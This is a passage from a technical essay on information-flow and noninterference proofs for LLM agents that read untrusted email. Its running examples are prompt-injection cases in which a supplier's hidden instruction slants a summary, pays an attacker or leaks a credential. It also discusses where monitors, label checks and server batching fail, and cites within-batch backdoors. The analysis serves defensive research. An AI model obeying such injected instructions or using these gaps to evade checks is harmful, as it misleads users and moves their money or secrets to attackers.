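A deeper obstacle is that a transformer's code reveals little about its behaviour. In ordinary software, a line such as `if balance > threshold` shows an analyser that what happens next depends on the balance. A transformer's code is much the same sequence of matrix operations whatever the model has learned. Because attention draws on all earlier positions, an analyser that followed labels through the arithmetic would mark every output after the email as untrusted, which FIDES already does without looking inside the model. Whether the model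 ignores or obeys an instruction depends on the values of its weights, which require a different kind of analysis.

The code around a model may not show whether a skill leaks data. In an example from *PACE* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026), a mail skill always calls the same function to send an email, and written instructions tell the model how to compose the body. One version of the instructions asks for a fixed template and another asks the model to copy a credential, such as a password, from its context, but the code and interface are the same in both. Li and colleagues prove that a reviewer who has the same evidence for a safe version and a leaking one can't soundly exempt either from checks when the email is sent.

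There is also no agreed specification of a harmful hidden state. Some bounds can be stated precisely without one, such as "no activation changes when the email changes" or a limit in bits or in distance. Bounds on what the state represents are harder to specify, because a planner must represent a hidden instruction whether it is going to obey it or has identified it as an attack and is going to refuse. A rule against representing the instruction would forbid the refusal as well as the obedience.

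Even specifications of observable behaviour are hard to get right. *Toward Safe LLM Agents* (Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues, 2026) reviewed 38 studies and concluded that specification is the main bottleneck. On one benchmark, when language models translated ordinary language into a formal planning language, only 24.8% to 34.2% of the translations had the right meaning. The review left out work on verifying neural networks unless it applied to agents' plans, so even surveys largely separate verifying networks from verifying agents' behaviour.

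Moon and Varshney had language models write the specifications for two small agents from a template. The template had no field for one agent's important effects. When the language model could also see that agent's code, it left the nearest field empty, so the safety condition applied to an empty list and was automatically true. Dafny accepted the proof, and the specification passed all three of Moon and Varshney's quality checks. If a mistake like this can go undetected in a specification of file reads and tool calls, a specification of what activations should represent would be much harder to trust.

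### Why an opaque model cannot be unwound

Security researchers have also tended to define security properties by what someone outside the system can see. SRI's *Computer security theory of noninterference*, for instance, defines noninterference entirely by the outputs that another part of the system later receives. By this definition, a change in the hidden state that never affects an output is not a security failure.

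Proofs of such properties nevertheless often refer to the system's internals. The definition covers action sequences of any length, which nobody can check one by one. *The Generic Unwinding Theorem for CSP Noninterference Security* (Noce, 2015) explains that unwinding replaces this task with checking conditions on individual actions. *Noninterference, Transitivity, and Channel-Control Security Policies* (Rushby, 1992) proves an unwinding theorem that also applies when information may travel only by an approved route. In Case C, for example, the email may influence the planner only through the quarantined model's answer.

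To use unwinding, one finds a relation between the system's internal states, written $s \approx t$, which means roughly that the difference between $s$ and $t$ will never matter to the observer. *Event-based Compositional Reasoning of Information-Flow Security for Concurrent Systems* (2023) lists three conditions to check. In their simplest form, with $s \cdot a$ for the state after action $a$, they are:

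$$s \approx t \;\Rightarrow\; \mathrm{obs}(s) = \mathrm{obs}(t)$$

$$s \approx s \cdot h \quad \text{for every action } h \text{ that must not affect the observer}$$

$$s \approx t \;\Rightarrow\; s \cdot a \approx t \cdot a \quad \text{for every action } a$$

Related states look the same to the observer, a hidden action leads to a related state, and related states stay related after any further action. By induction, hidden actions never change what the observer sees.

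Case B satisfies these conditions if the observer watches only payments. Two states are related if they differ only in the text stored under `email_0`, and the hidden action is the supplier replacing that text. The payments are the same in both states, and so is the planner's context, as with hidden variables in FIDES. With the same seed, every step therefore preserves the relation, and nobody has to examine the planner to prove it. The proof in *PerMIT* similarly relies on matching runs in which the planner has the same view and history.

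In case A, the two emails enter the planner's context, so this shortcut is unavailable. Anyone attempting the proof would have to define which hidden states count as related after the planner has read different emails, then prove that related states lead to the same payment decision and remain related after every further token. They cannot check either claim if the model is opaque. Open weights provide the exact rule for getting from one hidden state to the next, but not the relation, and finding one can take considerable ingenuity even for conventional systems.

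There is a relation that always works if the system is secure. In a proof in *Noninterference with Local Policies* (2012), two states are related exactly when the observer would see the same thing after every possible sequence of future actions:

$$s \approx t \quad\text{if and only if}\quad \mathrm{obs}(s \cdot \alpha) = \mathrm{obs}(t \cdot \alpha) \ \text{ for every sequence } \alpha$$

This guarantees that a relation exists, but it does not help with an opaque model, because checking whether two states are related requires knowing all their future outputs. It also does not limit how much related states can differ internally. Two hidden states with very different activations are related as long as the observer can never tell them apart.

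### Are checked actions enough?

Suppose the user now asks the assistant to summarise a supplier's record before a contract renewal. One of the supplier's emails contains a hidden instruction to describe the supplier's late deliveries as minor. The planner follows the instruction and sends the user a favourable summary. The tool is on the approved list, the recipient is correct, and the message has the right format, so a runtime that checks only these things lets the summary through.

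Moon and Varshney explicitly exclude this kind of failure. Their method covers what they call boundary-enforceable properties, which can be expressed in terms of typed actions, their arguments, the resulting events and the system's state. Truthfulness, deception and manipulation depend on what a text means, so they fall outside the method. *PerMIT* has a similar limit. Its term "trusted" refers to where a value came from and who approved it, so a trusted value can still be false.

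The case for checking actions anyway is that the worst failures of agents seem to require an action. Moon and Varshney list sending data to unauthorised destinations, moving money irreversibly, destroying files, altering databases and tampering with monitoring systems. If the interface offers no way to do these things, the agent cannot do them, whatever the model has read or is planning. An agent that can pay only accounts on file cannot pay the attacker's new account, even if the email has completely taken over its hidden state.

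The reply is that permitted text is itself an effect. In their definition of secrecy, Li and colleagues count the agent's final answer as one of the places where information leaves the system. They compare the answer's raw bytes, so a secret that has been translated or split into pieces still counts as a leak. In the supplier example, the task produces only a summary, and the harm comes from the user believing it.

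Checking actions is enough for the failures on Moon and Varshney's list if effect exclusivity holds and the policy is complete. Completeness is hard to achieve. Dantas and colleagues describe one study in which a system blocked 94% of unsafe actions, yet in most settings the agents completed fewer than 5% of tasks both safely and correctly, because they found other unsafe routes. Nobody has replicated the study, but it illustrates how a partial policy can block most unsafe actions and still leave the task unsafe.

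The reply is right about truthfulness and fairness. Whether the summary is slanted depends on how it compares with the supplier's record, and checks on the summary's recipient and format don't make that comparison. The runtime could ask another model to judge the summary, but a proof that treated this judge as an unconstrained oracle would have to assume that it might approve any summary. Integrity noninterference would rule out the slant, but only by preventing the summary from depending on the emails it is supposed to summarise. Narrowing the output helps only partly. In case C, the quarantined model can't write persuasive prose, but it can still answer "yes" when no crates have arrived.

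The runtime can only partly check whether a message reveals a secret. It can search an outgoing message for the user's balance, and Li and colleagues also search for encoded versions of protected values. They acknowledge that paraphrases, translations and values split across several pieces can escape this search. It is safer for the boundary to control what the model reads, by keeping the balance out of any context from which the model writes to the supplier.

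Content can also defeat a check on actions when the check relies on a person. If the slanted summary persuades the user to renew the contract, the renewal is properly authorised. The confirmation gate in *PerMIT* has the same weakness. It can display a quarantined model's summary word for word and record that the user accepted it, but the user still has to decide whether the summary is true.

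## When does a proof about the runtime also bound the hidden state?

The runtime controls much of what determines a model's hidden state, even though these proofs don't mention it. A model computes its hidden state from its weights, its context and, once it starts generating tokens, the random seed. A proof that limits how untrusted text can change the context therefore also limits how that text can change the hidden state. If the text never reaches the planner, it can't change the planner's hidden state at all. If the planner receives only a choice from a short list, the text can still affect the hidden state, but only through that choice.

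### Keeping the email out of the context

In case B, the planner receives the name `email_0` instead of the supplier's email. Let $c_j(x)$ be the context of the planner's $j$-th call when the email is $x$, with the user's request and all other trusted inputs held constant. Let $\omega_j$ be the random choices for that call, and $F$ the function that turns a context and random choices into activations. Then

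$$H_j(x) = F(c_j(x),\, \omega_j), \qquad c_j(x) = c_j(x') \;\Rightarrow\; H_j(x) = H_j(x')$$

The contexts match for the same reason that case B satisfies the unwinding conditions. The first context contains only the user's request and the tool descriptions, so the planner has the same hidden state in both runs and makes the same request. The runtime fetches a different email in each run but adds the same name to the conversation, so the next context is the same too, and so on until the run ends.

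The planner's hidden state is the same whatever the email contains, so all four kinds of bound hold. Its activations do not depend on the email, contain 0 bits of information about it, move zero distance when it changes, and represent the same things whichever email arrives. This is true even of a planner that would obey any instruction it read.

The argument assumes that the model depends only on its context and seed, which would be false if anything carried over from an earlier call. It also assumes that nothing the runtime adds to the context depends on the email, which is easy to get wrong. FIDES builds each variable name from the tool, a running number and the field, as in `#read_emails_0.subject`. If a runtime named variables after subject lines instead, the supplier could write into the planner's context.

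The number of variables can reveal information even when their names are neutral. When Costa and colleagues tested FIDES, it created a separate variable for each untrusted field of each email, so the planner could count the emails. A supplier who sent two emails instead of one would change the planner's hidden state without any of the text reaching it. Labelling the whole list as untrusted would avoid this, because FIDES would then store the list in a single variable.

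Refusals can also pass information to the planner. FIDES notifies the planner when a policy blocks a tool call, and a secrecy policy may allow only an email's sender and recipients to read it. The supplier's choice of whom to copy in could then affect whether the planner may forward the email to the accounts department, and the planner would receive the result.

### The proof's invariant and the theorem's statement

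The exclusion argument needs to know what the planner's context contains at each call. In LLMbda this comes from an invariant, a condition that the proof maintains throughout a run. To an observer who sees only trusted data, Garby and colleagues count two conversations $C$ and $C'$ as indistinguishable under the following condition:

$$C \sim C' \quad\text{if and only if}\quad C = C' \ \text{ or } \ C \text{ and } C' \text{ are both labelled untrusted}$$

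If the planner's conversation has a trusted label, its text is therefore the same in both runs. The email cannot enter while the label stays trusted, because the label covers everything sent to the conversation. The `fork` command copies the conversation and restores the original once the program has finished with the copy, so anything added only to the copy is discarded. The `clear` command empties the conversation and resets its label to that of the current branch of the program. A planner that has read the email can therefore start again with a trusted conversation, and its later hidden states no longer depend on the email.

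For any given program, the theorem guarantees less than this, because it compares only the final conversation and the final value. Suppose a program forks its conversation, sends the email to the copy, ignores the reply and returns "done". The final conversation and value are the same for every email, as the theorem requires, but the model call that processed the email had a different hidden state for each one. To find out whether a particular call is protected, one has to check the label on its conversation at the time of the call.

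FIDES also keeps a label for the planner's context. When a tool result would raise that label, the runtime stores the result and gives the planner a name for it instead. Costa and colleagues prove secrecy for values that tools write to a datastore, so the exclusion argument again relies on how the runtime builds the context. The argument fails once the planner inspects an email in full. The context is then untrusted, so adding the next email would not raise the label, and FIDES would not hide it.

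LLMbda's theorem compares probabilities, but the exclusion argument compares individual runs with the same seed. Garby and colleagues link the two by having their interpreter look up each reply in a table of replies sampled in advance. Which entry it uses depends on the conversation and on how many replies the run has already received.

Suppose one email makes a quarantined model give an unreadable reply, so the program calls it again. The planner's next call might then be the fifth in the run instead of the fourth, and it would use a different table entry for the same context. The planner's activations for that context would not change, because they involve no random draw, but it might generate different tokens, which have their own activations. The probabilities are the same either way, so an observer still could not learn anything about the email from the hidden state alone. Giving the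 planner its own sequence of random numbers would remove this difference. Exclusion also applies only to calls that both runs reach, since an email may still stop an LLMbda run.

Keeping the text out of the planner does not make the agent safe. The LLMbda agent tested on AgentDojo finishes its plan in a simulated world before running it on real data. The two successful attacks relied on an endorsed file, which the program read only after the planner had finished, so the file could not have affected the planner's hidden state.

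### Letting one of *k* values through

In case C, something about the email does reach the planner. Let $Z$ be the value that the runtime passes on, which is one of $k$ possible values, and let $t$ be the rest of the context, which does not depend on the email. For a fixed seed $\omega$, the hidden state is

$$H = F(c(t, Z),\, \omega)$$

Each value of $Z$ produces one hidden state, so there are at most $k$ of them. By the data-processing inequality,

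$$I(X;H \mid \omega) \;\le\; I(X;Z \mid \omega) \;\le\; \log_2 k$$

The bound holds however the attacker chooses the email. In the supplier example, the planner's hidden state is the same for every email until the answer arrives. After that, the hidden state can take at most three values, so it carries at most 1.58 bits of information about the email, which is also the limit for the answer.

The value of $k$ has to include every way the quarantined call can end. *SPA* (2026) describes an agent whose quarantined model must fit its reply to a schema, a fixed description of the allowed outputs. The model is instructed to return an explicit failure value, if the schema has one, when it can't complete its task. In case C, that value is "unclear". If the runtime could also report that the call had timed out, there would be four possible values and the bound would rise to 2 bits.

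Suppose the user has ten suppliers and the agent asks the same question, with three possible answers, about one email from each. There are at most $3^{10} = 59{,}049$ combinations of answers, so the planner's final hidden state carries at most 15.85 bits about the ten emails together. The bound still holds if the planner uses earlier answers to decide what to ask next, as long as it always receives ten answers with three possible values each, because each answer multiplies the number of possible contexts by at most three.

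### When the email also affects the number, order or timing of calls

The count of 59,049 assumes that the emails affect only the answers. If they can also determine when the agent stops asking, the planner may receive anything from zero to ten answers. The number of possible contexts is then

$$1 + 3 + 3^2 + \cdots + 3^{10} = 88{,}573$$

which corresponds to 16.4 bits. The increase is small here because there is a maximum of ten answers. Without a maximum, the number of contexts has no limit.

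Retries can have a larger effect. Suppose the agent repeats a question whenever the answer is "unclear", up to 1,000 times, and keeps every answer in the planner's context. An attacker who controls the quarantined model could choose how many times it answers "unclear" before it answers "yes" or "no". There are 2,001 possible sequences of answers, so the answers to this one question can carry almost 11 bits.

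Injections can change the number of calls even when the planner fixed its plan in advance. *Relativising Integrity and Robustness* (2026) analyses a banking task in AgentDojo in which a bill includes an instruction to pay the attacker as well. The plan contains a single payment command, but the agent makes two payments, the first to the attacker. If the runtime reported each payment to the planner, the number of reports would depend on the text of the bill.

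The order of the answers can carry information too. FIDES makes one tool call at a time, but Costa and colleagues mention that parallel calls could make such systems faster. If ten quarantined calls ran in parallel and the runtime listed each answer, with the supplier's name, as it arrived, there would be $10!$ possible orders. The order could then carry up to 21.8 bits, raising the total from 15.8 bits to at most 37.6. An attacker could influence the order by slowing down a quarantined model, for example by giving it a long calculation. The runtime can prevent this by waiting for all ten answers and listing them in the order of the questions.

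Timing is harder to exclude, and Costa and colleagues leave it out of their formal guarantee. Suppose the context shows the time of each message to the second, and an email can change when a call finishes within a one-minute range. The timestamp then has 60 possible values and can carry up to 5.9 bits of information about the email. In case B, the planner never reads the emails, but timestamps would still carry information about them if longer emails took longer to forward.

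### What a small number of bits leaves open

A limit in bits does not limit the distance between hidden states. Suppose the planner prepares a payment after "yes" and writes a complaint to the supplier after "no". A single bit can select between the two resulting hidden states, whether they are almost identical or very far apart.

A bound on how many bits reach the planner also doesn't limit what its hidden states represent. Costa and colleagues suggest letting a quarantined model choose from a list of tasks such as `schedule_meeting`, `out_of_office_reply` and `forward_email`. An attacker who makes it choose `forward_email` can put the planner into a state of preparing to forward an email. With these three options, the choice carries at most 1.58 bits, the same as a choice among three harmless words.

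The count does stop the attacker from creating a state outside the list. If the trusted context and the seed are fixed, a developer could run the planner on all three possible answers and examine each hidden state in advance. Doing this for 59,049 combinations would take much longer but would still be possible. A count therefore leaves a finite number of states, but someone still has to examine their content.

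The bound on the planner's hidden state also doesn't limit the email's effect on the agent's actions. In another example from Costa and colleagues, the planner receives only a yes-or-no value for whether an email contains a meeting request, and refers to the meeting details by name when it calls the calendar tool. Its hidden state therefore carries at most 1 bit about the email, but the calendar entry can contain text the attacker wrote.

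There is no useful bound on the quarantined model's hidden state. The model reads the whole email, and its hidden state includes an embedding for every token. If different tokens have different embeddings, these identify the email exactly, which can amount to about 15,600 bits for 1,000 tokens from a vocabulary of 50,000. Restricting the answer to three words does not help, because the restriction applies when the model samples its answer, after it has computed the activations. The data-processing inequality does not help either, because it shows only that the hidden state carries at least as much information about the email as the answer does. In *SPA*, the quarantined model has no tools and no memory of the plan, which limits the harm it can do but not what it computes from the email.

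### Two ways to allow small values

Garby and colleagues call FIDES's exception for yes-or-no values and other small types defensible but hard to audit. A reviewer who sees such a value pass a policy check in a particular run cannot tell whether the designer meant to allow it or whether it is a leak.

The types in FIDES also don't keep a running total of bits. When FIDES combines two pieces of data, it joins their types, and joining "yes or no" with "yes or no" gives "yes or no" again. Ten such answers can produce 1,024 different contexts, but their combined type is the same as for one answer, so a policy that relies on the type may treat 10 bits as 1.

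LLMbda requires an explicit `endorse` command for each exception, so a reviewer can find them all in the program. Garby and colleagues describe a `bounded_endorse` function that accepts only values from a fixed list. It first makes a trusted copy of the value and then checks whether the copy is on the list. Checking the untrusted original first would make that branch untrusted, and an `endorse` command in an untrusted branch has no effect. Garby and colleagues leave a formal proof of the resulting limit in bits for future work.

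If a value is not on the list, `bounded_endorse` returns it unchanged and still labelled untrusted. This protects a payment tool that accepts only trusted values, but not the planner, because LLMbda lets a program send untrusted text to a trusted conversation as long as the conversation's label rises. If a quarantined model returned a paragraph instead of "yes", the whole paragraph could therefore enter the planner's context, and the count would no longer apply. To bound the hidden state, the program should replace any unlisted answer with a default such as "unclear".

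Endorsement also changes what a trusted label implies about the hidden state. Without it, a trusted conversation is the same for every email. After the program endorses an answer with three possible values and sends it to the planner, there are three possible conversations, all labelled trusted. Garby and colleagues describe a variant that permanently marks every endorsed value and never endorses a marked value, to stop one endorsement from leading to another. The mark would also show whether the exclusion argument still applies to a planner's context or whether one has to count the possible values.

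`bounded_endorse` would reject an account number or a payment amount because such values do not fit on a short list. Garby and colleagues argue that the user's instruction to pay the bill in the file justifies trusting such a value. If the planner passes the value by name instead of reading it, the value does not count towards the bound on the planner's hidden state.

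## What if the model's state outlasts the visible context?

Exclusion and counting both treat a model call as a function of its context and seed. This can be wrong even though applications resend the whole conversation with every request, because the server that runs the model may also save intermediate results, process several customers' requests together, or load new weights from one month to the next. If the supplier's email affects any of these, it can change the planner's hidden state without appearing in the planner's context.

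### The assumption in full

Let $e_j(x)$ stand for everything the planner's $j$-th call uses apart from its context and seed, such as the weights, saved activations and other requests on the same processor. The hidden state is then

$$H_j(x) = F(c_j(x),\, \omega_j,\, e_j(x))$$

and the statelessness assumption is

$$F(c, \omega, e_j(x)) = F(c, \omega, e_j(x')) \quad \text{for all } c, \omega, x, x'$$

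This holds if the email never changes $e_j$, or changes it only in ways that do not affect the activations. *Detent* (Xin, Feng and colleagues, 2026) uses a similar function to describe a model server. The function's output depends on the prompt, seed, weights, deployment, settings and a "batch state", which includes the requests running alongside and whether the server found part of the prompt in its cache.

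A violation may weaken a bound without destroying it. If $e_j$ can differ in $m$ ways that matter, the number of possible hidden states grows by at most a factor of $m$, so a bound remains only if $m$ has a known limit. With $m = 2$, the limit rises from 1.58 to 2.58 bits in case C and from 0 bits to 1 in case B.

### What a new session has to clear

Dongol lists seven conditions that a deployment must meet for the PlanTERS theorems to apply. Most concern the runtime. For example, every tool call must pass through the monitor. The "fresh sessions" condition also concerns the model. When a plan executes `NewSession`, the deployment must clear everything the model retains from untrusted content, including anything outside the visible context.

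PlanTERS cannot represent a model that retains untrusted text after a new session starts. It describes the model's context as a list of the untrusted items read in the current session, and `NewSession` empties that list. `NewSession` does not reset the model's internal state, but that state changes at every step by a fixed rule that takes no text as input. Whoever deploys the agent must establish whether the real model also retains no text from earlier sessions.

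The condition matters most when an agent gets its tools back. Suppose an assistant works through ten suppliers' emails, losing its sending tool whenever it reads one and regaining it before the next. Dongol proves such an agent secure against the paper's example attack if each email gets a fresh session. A similar agent that regains the tool while the old email is still in its context can leak, because the model can follow the old email's instruction and use the tool. If a server kept some information from the email after `NewSession`, the first agent could behave like the second, and nothing in the trace of observable events would show that the information had been kept.

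### Written memory

Text most obviously outlasts a session when the agent saves it. In an example from *SPA*, a user asks an agent on Monday to retrieve an invoice and keep the details, and on Tuesday to "pay the invoice we discussed yesterday". If an attacker has hidden an instruction in the invoice and the runtime puts the saved text into Tuesday's context, the planner's hidden state on Tuesday depends on what the attacker wrote.

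A label can follow this route because the runtime does the writing and the reading. SPA stores each result with its label and restores the label on retrieval. Later planners see only the result's format, its purpose and the query that produced it. An earlier planner wrote the purpose from trusted inputs, so none of the invoice's text reaches the new planner. But a small channel may remain, because SPA saves results only after a query succeeds, and it ends a query if a quarantined model's answer has the wrong format. An invoice that caused such a failure would leave no entry, so Tuesday's planner could learn one bit about the invoice from whether the entry exists.

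The SPA paper tests reuse across queries by splitting 97 AgentDojo tasks into conversations of two to five turns. With the information-flow checks off, attacks succeeded in 0.3% of runs when later planners saw only descriptions of the stored values, and in 0.6% when they saw the values themselves. The paper acknowledges that its attack only weakly tests instructions that lie dormant in memory, so this small difference is weak evidence that hiding the values is unnecessary. With the checks on, attacks succeeded in 0.2% of runs, but the share of tasks completed when there was no attack fell from 62.5% to 35.3%.

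In PerMIT, Jiang and colleagues' memory system, a user's confirmation outlasts the session, so the agent can later recall the confirmed value and use it with the same tool without asking again. In the shared version, enough confirmations from other people let a new user's agent use an item that the new user has never checked. A bound on the planner's hidden state would therefore have to account for everything admitted in earlier sessions, possibly by other users. No attacks succeeded against PerMIT on Trojan Hippo, a benchmark of dormant attacks, when the agent's own model or a lightweight verifier made the confirmation decisions. This result is evidence about the agent's actions, and confirmed text still changes the activations of any planner that reads it.

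### Saved keys and values

For each token, attention computes a key and a value. The key helps determine how much weight later positions give that token, and the value is what they receive from it. Servers save both to avoid recomputing them for each new token. Many also reuse them across requests that begin with the same text, such as a long system prompt.

This reuse doesn't violate statelessness if the cache is correct. The keys and values at one position depend only on the model and the tokens up to that position. If the server looks them up by the exact model and the complete sequence of those tokens, it gets the same numbers it would have computed. The reply arrives sooner, which may reveal to an observer that an earlier request began the same way. Dongol and *SPA* both leave such side channels out of scope. But the timing affects the planner's hidden state only if the runtime puts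 it into the context, for example as a timestamp.

An incorrect cache lookup, however, could insert activations from one conversation into another. This could happen if the server ignored which fine-tuned version of a model had produced a cache entry, or matched only part of the preceding text. The runtime's labels could not track those activations, because neither the entry nor the lookup is visible to the runtime.

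Even a correct cache can change the last digits of a calculation. Computers store these numbers with limited precision and round after each addition, so the order of the additions matters:

$$(0.1 + 10^{20}) - 10^{20} = 0, \qquad 0.1 + (10^{20} - 10^{20}) = 0.1$$

*Defeating Nondeterminism in LLM Inference*, a 2025 article by the AI company Thinking Machines Lab, gives an example with 80 saved tokens and 48 new ones. A program that adds them up in blocks of 32 uses four blocks if it handles all 128 together, but five if it handles the saved and new tokens separately. The different grouping can change the rounding. In case B, a long email processed by another model on the same server might push the planner's saved entries out of a full cache, so the planner's next call would group its additions differently. A server can avoid this by arranging saved and new entries in the same layout before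 attention begins.

### Requests processed together

Servers usually process many requests in one batch, and the size of the batch often determines how the processor divides its sums. Zhao, Yang and colleagues (2026), in *CoRun*, illustrate this with a row of four numbers. A processor with only one row to add may split the work and compute $(a+b)+(c+d)$, but with four rows it may add each row from left to right. The two results would be equal in exact arithmetic but can differ after rounding.

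Fixing the seed does not remove this batch effect. *God Does Not Play Dice* (2026) distinguishes it from run-to-run nondeterminism, where the same request in the same batch gives different results. The paper describes a common cause of that nondeterminism as rare when models generate text. Repeating the whole batch reproduces the batch effect, but a customer controls only one request in the batch.

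These differences can change the model's output. Thinking Machines Lab asked a large Qwen model the same question about Richard Feynman 1,000 times, with the model always choosing its most probable token, and got 80 different answers. All 1,000 answers were identical for the first 102 tokens, after which 992 gave Feynman's birthplace as "Queens, New York" and eight as "New York City". When the company replaced the relevant calculations with versions that added numbers in the same order regardless of the batch, all 1,000 answers were identical. Xin and colleagues found that changing only the load on a standard server changed the answers to 33 of 1,319 school mathematics problems.

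Thinking Machines Lab says the cause is not information leaking across the batch, which is right in the sense that the calculation for one request never uses the words of another. But noninterference requires slightly more than that. If the quarantined model and the planner share a server, a longer email can change the size of a batch, and with it the rounding in the planner's activations. The difference is tiny at first, but a changed token can make it much larger. An attacker would have trouble exploiting this, since other customers' traffic also changes the batch. Still, exclusion is meant to guarantee identical activations, and on such a server they may differ.

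Two recent systems restore the promise for a fixed deployment. Zhao and colleagues guarantee the same output $Y$ for a prompt $p$ and seed $s$, whatever other requests $\mathcal{C}$ are running, whatever the request's position $i$ in the batch and whatever the order of arrival $a$:

$$Y(p, s;\, \mathcal{C}, i, a) = Y(p, s;\, \mathcal{C}', i', a')$$

They process each prompt on its own and then generate tokens in batches padded to a constant size. They also tie the random numbers to the request, because its draw might otherwise change if it moved within the batch. The guarantee is stated only for output tokens, but its proof shows that the request's internal state also stays the same at every step, which exclusion requires. The guarantee does not cover changes of hardware, software version or number format.

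Xin and colleagues keep the order of additions constant by fixing the few batch-dependent values that determine which calculation routine the server uses. Their guarantee assumes that each routine is itself unaffected by the batch.

Servers don't do this by default because it slows them down. In one measurement by Zhao and colleagues, generating a token for each of 32 requests took 19.4 milliseconds normally, 88.4 with batch-independent routines and 32.6 with their own system. Xin and colleagues report delays per token of 1.04 to 1.17 times the standard, compared with 1.67 to 10.3 times for the existing deterministic modes. *LLM-42* (2026) suggests that such slowdowns may be why deterministic inference is largely confined to debugging and verification.

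### When another request's content matters

Both guarantees concern models in which, apart from rounding, each request's output depends only on its own input. Some mixture-of-experts models lack this property. In a mixture-of-experts model, a layer contains many feed-forward networks, called experts, and a router decides which experts process each token. Routing preserves the property if the router considers each token separately. Xin and colleagues' tests included a mixture-of-experts model.

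Requests can also affect each other by competing for an expert's limited places. *Stealing User Prompts from Mixture of Experts* (2024) describes expert-choice routing, in which each expert selects a fixed number of tokens from the whole batch and some tokens may get no expert. *Capacity-Aware Inference* (2025) studies a related design that gives each expert a maximum load and drops the excess tokens, which in one version are the later ones. Whether an expert processes a word in the planner's context can then depend on the supplier's email, if both are in the same batch. A consistent order of additions would not prevent this, because the calculation itself changes.

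Labels can detect some of these connections if they travel through the model's own arithmetic. Küchler, Petrov and colleagues (2025), in *Architectural Backdoors for Within-Batch Data Stealing and Model Inference Manipulation*, built a checker that gives each user's input a numbered label and follows it through every operation in a model file. It stores only the smallest and largest label that may have influenced each number. When two numbers combine, their labels combine as

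$$(a,b) \star (c,d) = (\min(a,c),\, \max(b,d))$$

A number influenced only by user 3 has the label $(3,3)$. Adding a number influenced by user 7 gives a sum with the label $(3,7)$, and the checker detects that data from different users has mixed because the two entries differ. If every output has only its own user's label, the checker has proved noninterference between the users in the batch.

Such labels don't help within a single context, because attention mixes everything in it. Different users' data should not mix at all, though, so a conservative label can still be useful for checking that it stays separate.

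Küchler and colleagues ran the checker on 1,680 model files from the Hugging Face hub and proved 361 free of leaks between users. The checker found a leak in another 269, because a method of compressing numbers set its scale from the smallest and largest values in the entire batch. They describe this leak as potentially difficult to exploit. The remaining 1,050 files were neither proved free of leaks nor found to have one. The checker requires the size of every array in advance and a rule for every operation, and a proof covers only the input sizes examined. It also follows the calculation written in the file, so a file can pass even if the server runs it with a routine whose rounding depends on the batch.

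### Passing activations between models

A system could also let models exchange activations instead of words. Suppose the quarantined model in case C gave the planner a vector of 768 numbers, each stored in 16 bits, instead of "yes", "no" or "unclear". The vector could carry up to 12,288 bits, and it would change the planner's hidden state by design.

The runtime could label the whole vector untrusted if it handled the transfer. The usual exceptions would be harder to justify, because a person at a confirmation gate can't read a list of activations, and a rule that accepts any 768 numbers restricts almost nothing. A vector can also change the model's behaviour directly. Küchler and colleagues describe earlier research in which adding a precomputed vector to a model's activations made it refuse a harmless request. To make the bit count useful again, the runtime could replace each vector with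 the nearest of $k$ approved ones, which would limit it to $\log_2 k$ bits.

### Training on untrusted text

Suppose a company fine-tunes its planner every month on records of past tasks, including suppliers' emails. The planner in case B may never receive a supplier's email in its context, but its weights depend on emails from previous months. Every later hidden state can depend on those emails too, and neither `NewSession` nor an empty cache will remove their influence.

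*Information Flow Control in Machine Learning through Modular Model Architecture* (2023) extends noninterference to this case. It divides the training data into domains and gives each user access to some of them. Let $D$ and $D'$ be two training sets that agree on every domain the user may access, and let $M_D$ be the model trained on $D$. The natural requirement is that the model give this user the same probabilities for every query $q$:

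$$M_D(q) = M_{D'}(q) \quad \text{whenever } D \text{ and } D' \text{ agree on the permitted domains}$$

For integrity, the permitted domains would be the trusted ones. Ordinary fine-tuning makes the property hard to satisfy because each training example can affect every updated weight. The only safe label for the resulting model is the join of the labels on all its training data, so if any of that data is untrusted, everything the model produces is untrusted too. Separate modules for separate domains allow finer labels, as long as a trusted request never uses a module trained on untrusted text. Removing emails that contain visible instructions would not satisfy the definition, because an ordinary delivery note also changes the weights.

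### What an operator would have to establish

The operator of the payment assistant would have to account for everything in $e_j$. For the weights, the operator would have to show that no untrusted text from the period covered by the proof has entered the planner's training, and that the provider cannot switch to a newly trained version unannounced. Stored memory must keep its labels, including any memory that the provider adds on its own servers. The cache must key each entry on everything that affects it, and the server must produce the same activations whether or not it finds an entry.

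Batching requires both kinds of check described above. The model must keep each request's content out of the other requests' calculations, and the server must perform additions in the same order under any load. Running the planner alone would avoid both problems but lose the efficiency of batching.

A company that rents a model through an online service can verify very little of this. It can send the same request many times under different loads, and a changed answer would show that something besides the context and seed affects the output. Identical answers would not prove that nothing else does, so the company must rely on the provider's account of how it runs the model.

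## Why does safe behaviour not show that untrusted text left the hidden state alone?

Even a perfectly stateless server does not help in case A, where the planner reads the supplier's email. Exclusion fails because the email is in the context, and counting fails because the number of possible emails is enormous. Even if the agent takes the same actions whatever the email contains, the email may still have changed the model's hidden state. By the data-processing inequality, the actions carry at most as much information about the email as the hidden state does, so showing that the actions carry none puts no upper limit on what the hidden state carries.

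### What the actions can prove

In case A, the inequality gives $I(X;H) \ge I(X;A)$. Measuring how much the actions reveal about the email therefore gives a lower limit on what the hidden state holds. If the permitted actions carry 0.53 bits about the email, the planner's hidden state carries at least 0.53 bits. If the actions carry nothing, the inequality becomes

$$I(X;H) \ge 0$$

which is true of any two quantities. A noninterference proof for payments establishes the zero on the right for every possible email, which no amount of testing could do, but the limit on the hidden state is still "at least zero".

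When a monitor blocks a tool call, such as a request to pay, the runtime refuses the request after the planner has computed its activations and output the request. The refusal can reduce $I(X;A)$ to zero, but it cannot change the activations that produced the request. A stricter monitor would affect a later planner call only if the runtime told the planner about the refusal.

In AgentSecBench, Alpay and Alpay separate these effects by recording whether a defence removed the forbidden text before the model received it, as well as whether the model then misbehaved. Let $q$ be the probability that the text remains visible to the model, and let $p_{\text{open}}$ and $p_{\text{closed}}$ be the probabilities of a forbidden request with the text visible and removed. If a check on the output misses at most a fraction $r$ of forbidden requests, then

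$$\text{risk of a forbidden action} \;\le\; r\,\big(q\,p_{\text{open}} + (1-q)\,p_{\text{closed}}\big)$$

In case A, $q = 1$. If the planner follows a hidden instruction 10% of the time and the check misses one forbidden request in 100, the risk is at most 0.1%. A check that misses one in 10,000 lowers that bound to 0.001%, but $q$ is still 1 and the planner still reads all the untrusted text.

Test results may not even show that the observable flow is zero. Alpay and Alpay search the model's output for an exact marker, such as a planted secret string, and acknowledge that this search would miss a paraphrase.

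### A bit that the output ignores

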